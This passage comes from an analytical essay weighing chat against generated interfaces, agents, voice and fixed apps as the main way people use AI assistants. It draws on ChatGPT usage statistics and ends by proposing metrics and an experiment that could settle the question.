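- **October 7:** Intelligent UI launched, but only in the Chat tab.
- **October 28:** Some American Pro users could start texting their dot through iMessage or RCS, the two standard phone messaging systems. A dot can also text first.

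Three weeks after adding its most elaborate screens to chat, OpenAI put its most independent agent in an ordinary text thread. This is fairly good evidence that users can instruct agents, and agents can send short updates, without generated interfaces. It is also evidence that chat survives, because a text thread is nearly the purest form of chat.

The absence of Intelligent UI from Work and Codex is weaker evidence. OpenAI may not have added it yet, and Work has its own visual output, including slides and interactive pages. People who use agents also need to check what the agents did. Suppose a dot texts "Renewed your car insurance for $640, saving $90." If the excess, the part of a claim that the driver pays, has risen from $250 to $1,000, one accident would cost the driver $750 more. The message is true, but a table comparing the old and new policies would have shown the problem. Agents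 probably reduce the time people spend looking at screens during a task, but make a good display of the results more useful at the end.

Voice has a similar imbalance. As rough averages, people type 40 words a minute on a phone, speak 150 and read 240. A 40-word request takes a minute to type and 16 seconds to say, so voice is much faster for asking. But a 300-word answer takes 75 seconds to read and two minutes to hear, and a listener comparing phones can't glance back at the second one's battery life. OpenAI's voice mode lets people follow written responses in the chat when they use plugins, which suggests that speech works best for requests and a screen for replies.

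Software engineers quickly found work for agents, but according to *Meet the OpenAI Engineer Leading ChatGPT's Biggest Transformation Yet*, consumers didn't really know what to do with OpenAI's earlier ones. Sottiaux's answer is to start with something small and build confidence from there. Users have the same problem with chat's blank box, but it is harder with an agent because they have to think of a whole task to hand over and trust it to go well.

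### Starting, refining and coming back

The four positions are easier to compare at particular moments in a task.

| | Starting | Refining | Coming back |
|---|---|---|---|
| Chat with interfaces as answers | Type or say the request | Use the controls, or send a message | Reopen the conversation or ask again |
| An end to the chat box | Use controls that fit the situation, with chat as a fallback | Use the controls, which change with the task | Get a new interface for the same goal |
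| Fixed interfaces | Open a familiar app or tab | Use familiar controls | Find everything where it was |
| Agents and voice | Hand over the task, or let an event trigger it | Correct the agent in words | Wait for the agent to report |

The generated interfaces released so far have changed little about how people start a task. Belshaw contrasts an ordinary app, which people go to and whose layout they learn, with an app inside ChatGPT, which the model calls up in the middle of a conversation. Someone using an app inside ChatGPT stays in the conversation and still begins by saying something.

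Automations and suggested messages are a greater threat to chat as a starting point than generated interfaces are. On September 29, ChatGPT began letting a change in a connected app start an automation, such as writing a summary whenever something new arrives in a work channel. The user writes the instruction once and may never type it again. Codex has also begun suggesting the user's next message, which some Pro users can accept with the Tab key. They still send a message, but they only have to approve it.

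AI can also be built into other products, where people use it without noticing. Dodds quotes the analyst Benedict Evans, who asks whether people will mostly use language models as chatbots or inside other products, as they use databases. Google's AI Overviews already work somewhat like this, since many of their 2.5 billion monthly users only meant to search the web. ChatGPT's 1.2 billion users are counted weekly, so the two figures aren't directly comparable. Chat may no longer have the most users, but it very likely still leads in time spent and difficulty of questions.

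Generated interfaces change user input most when people refine a result. Someone comparing loan terms can move a slider instead of sending a series of messages. Words are still better for changes that the controls don't cover. A borrower who wonders "what if I'm out of work for six months?" has to ask, unless the model included a switch for it. So controls will probably replace chat for small adjustments, but not for harder ones.

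The disagreement is sharpest over tools that people want to use again. A person who starts three conversations a day has 1,095 after a year, and a useful budget tool in one of them is hard to find by scrolling. If they ask the AI to make the tool again, they lose their old entries. thirteen23's dissolving interface is fine for someone who needs an insight only once, but the supporters of fixed interfaces have a much stronger case for a monthly budget. OpenAI's tabs and Anthropic's saved artifacts suggest that both companies agree.

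An agent could watch the budget and send a text when spending gets too high, so the user wouldn't have to come back to check it. That would suit people who want to know only when something is wrong, but those who want to see where the money went would still need a screen.

### What people use ChatGPT for

Data on what people ask ChatGPT can help test views about interfaces. OpenAI's 2025 study covered more than a million conversations. United Nations University's *What over 2.5 Billion Daily Messages Reveal About ChatGPT Use* reports that users asked for advice or information in 49% of messages, asked ChatGPT to perform a task in 40%, and expressed something without wanting a particular result in 11%. OpenAI concluded that people value ChatGPT "most as an advisor", according to ITPro's *OpenAI just revealed what people really use ChatGPT for*.

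This is moderately good news for chat as input, since advice usually depends on circumstances that people have to describe. It is less encouraging for agents, because the 40% includes requests that don't need an agent, such as writing an email, which ChatGPT finishes in seconds without a cloud computer.

In *Writing drops from 34% to 21% of ChatGPT requests since July 2024*, Rijo (2026) reports the newest figures from OpenAI's data. Practical advice is now the largest category, at 28.1% of requests, while coding help has fallen to 4.6%. Practical advice includes workout plans, tutoring and how-to questions, the kinds of request OpenAI used to demonstrate Intelligent UI. Writing requests suit a generated interface less well because the person wants the text itself.

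These are shares, so they don't show that people write less with ChatGPT. A fall from 34% to 21% means fewer writing requests only if total requests grew by less than about 60%, and ChatGPT has almost certainly grown faster than that since July 2024. *ChatGPT work requests fall to 32.2% as writing loses its top spot* (Rijo, 2026) reports that work's share of consumer requests fell from 51.6% to 32.2%, which likewise doesn't show that people make fewer work requests. Most of that fall may have happened by 2025, when an ITPro headline put 70% of queries outside work. That would leave about 30% for work, if both figures define work in the same way.

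The drop in coding help is the most interesting figure for the agent argument, because some programmers have probably taken their questions to Codex and its rivals. If so, people leave ordinary chat once an agent can do the job. But they still instruct Codex by typing messages in a thread, so even here the change is mostly in what they get back.

Rutgers University's *State of the Prompt*, a study from outside OpenAI, gives a slightly different picture. It covers 3.4 million ChatGPT conversations from July 2025 to June 2026, shared by 73,852 Americans. Health was the largest of 28 subjects, at one conversation in ten, and its share rose to about one in eight at 5 and 6 in the morning. Some of these conversations would benefit from a chart, such as one about three months of blood pressure readings. But a person awake at five with a worrying symptom probably wants to describe it and answer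 questions about it, and may not want to do so aloud if somebody is asleep nearby. The participants volunteered, so they may differ from other users.

None of this research sorts messages by whether an interface would have helped, but a rough range is possible. United Nations University's *What over 2.5 billion daily messages reveal about how people use ChatGPT* puts information-seeking at 24% of messages in 2025. Excluding both information-seeking and practical advice leaves about 48% of messages.

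| | Cautious guess | Generous guess |
|---|---|---|
| Practical advice (28.1%) | One in five suits an interface | Seven in ten |
| Seeking information (24%) | One in ten | Half |
| Everything else (about 48%) | None | One in ten |
| Share of all messages | 8% | 36% |

The fractions are guesses, and the topic shares come from different years. Even with the generous fractions, nearly two thirds of messages would still be answered in plain text. In the follow-up study by Chen and colleagues, people who judged answers to their own questions preferred the interface about half the time, well above the range estimated here. But they submitted complete questions, while real conversations include many messages such as "shorter, please" that no interface would improve.

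ChatGPT Images 2.0 is the one precedent for a new kind of output changing what people ask for. After it came out in April 2026, multimedia became the fastest-growing use and reached 7.8% of messages worldwide, according to OpenAI's *How the world is putting ChatGPT to work*. If calculators and diagrams have a similar effect, people will begin asking questions they wouldn't have brought to a text chatbot, and estimates based on old conversations will be too low. The effect may be smaller than it was for pictures, though, because people already knew they wanted pictures.

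### Figures that would settle it

OpenAI's public usage data runs to the end of September 2026, a week before Intelligent UI launched. The next release should cover the feature's first months, but the usual figures could easily be misleading because they count messages.

Suppose 281 of every thousand messages are about practical advice, and generated interfaces make a quarter of those unnecessary because people move a slider instead of writing again. That leaves 211 out of 930, so the share of advice falls from 28.1% to 22.7%. People would still be getting advice, with less typing, but the lower share could be mistaken for a loss of interest. A fall in the total number of messages could similarly be mistaken for people abandoning chat.

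These figures would be more useful:

| Figure | What it would show |
|---|---|
| Share of new tasks that begin with a typed or spoken request | If it stays above, say, 80%, chat survives as input. A fall below half would mean that the box really is ending as the main form. |
| Uses of a control for each follow-up message, in conversations that contain an interface | A high number would mean that controls have taken over refinement. A number near zero would mean that people look at the interfaces and go on typing. |
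| Share of generated tools that people reopen within a month, and the share they request again from scratch | Frequent reopening favours permanent places. Frequent repeat requests favour temporary tools, unless people ask again only because they can't find the old one. |
| Share of people outside software who give an agent a task every week | A rise from a few percent to a third within two years would support Sottiaux. |
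| Share of agents' results that people accept without opening anything to check them | A high share would mean less need for screens, provided the mistakes stayed rare. |

OpenAI and Google could probably calculate most of these from records they already keep. Testing the case for fixed layouts also requires an experiment. Researchers could ask two groups to update a household budget every week for two months. One group would use a generated screen that stays the same, and the other would use a screen that the model remakes each time. If the second group were still slower in the eighth week, companies would have a good reason to save a generated layout as soon as somebody used it twice.
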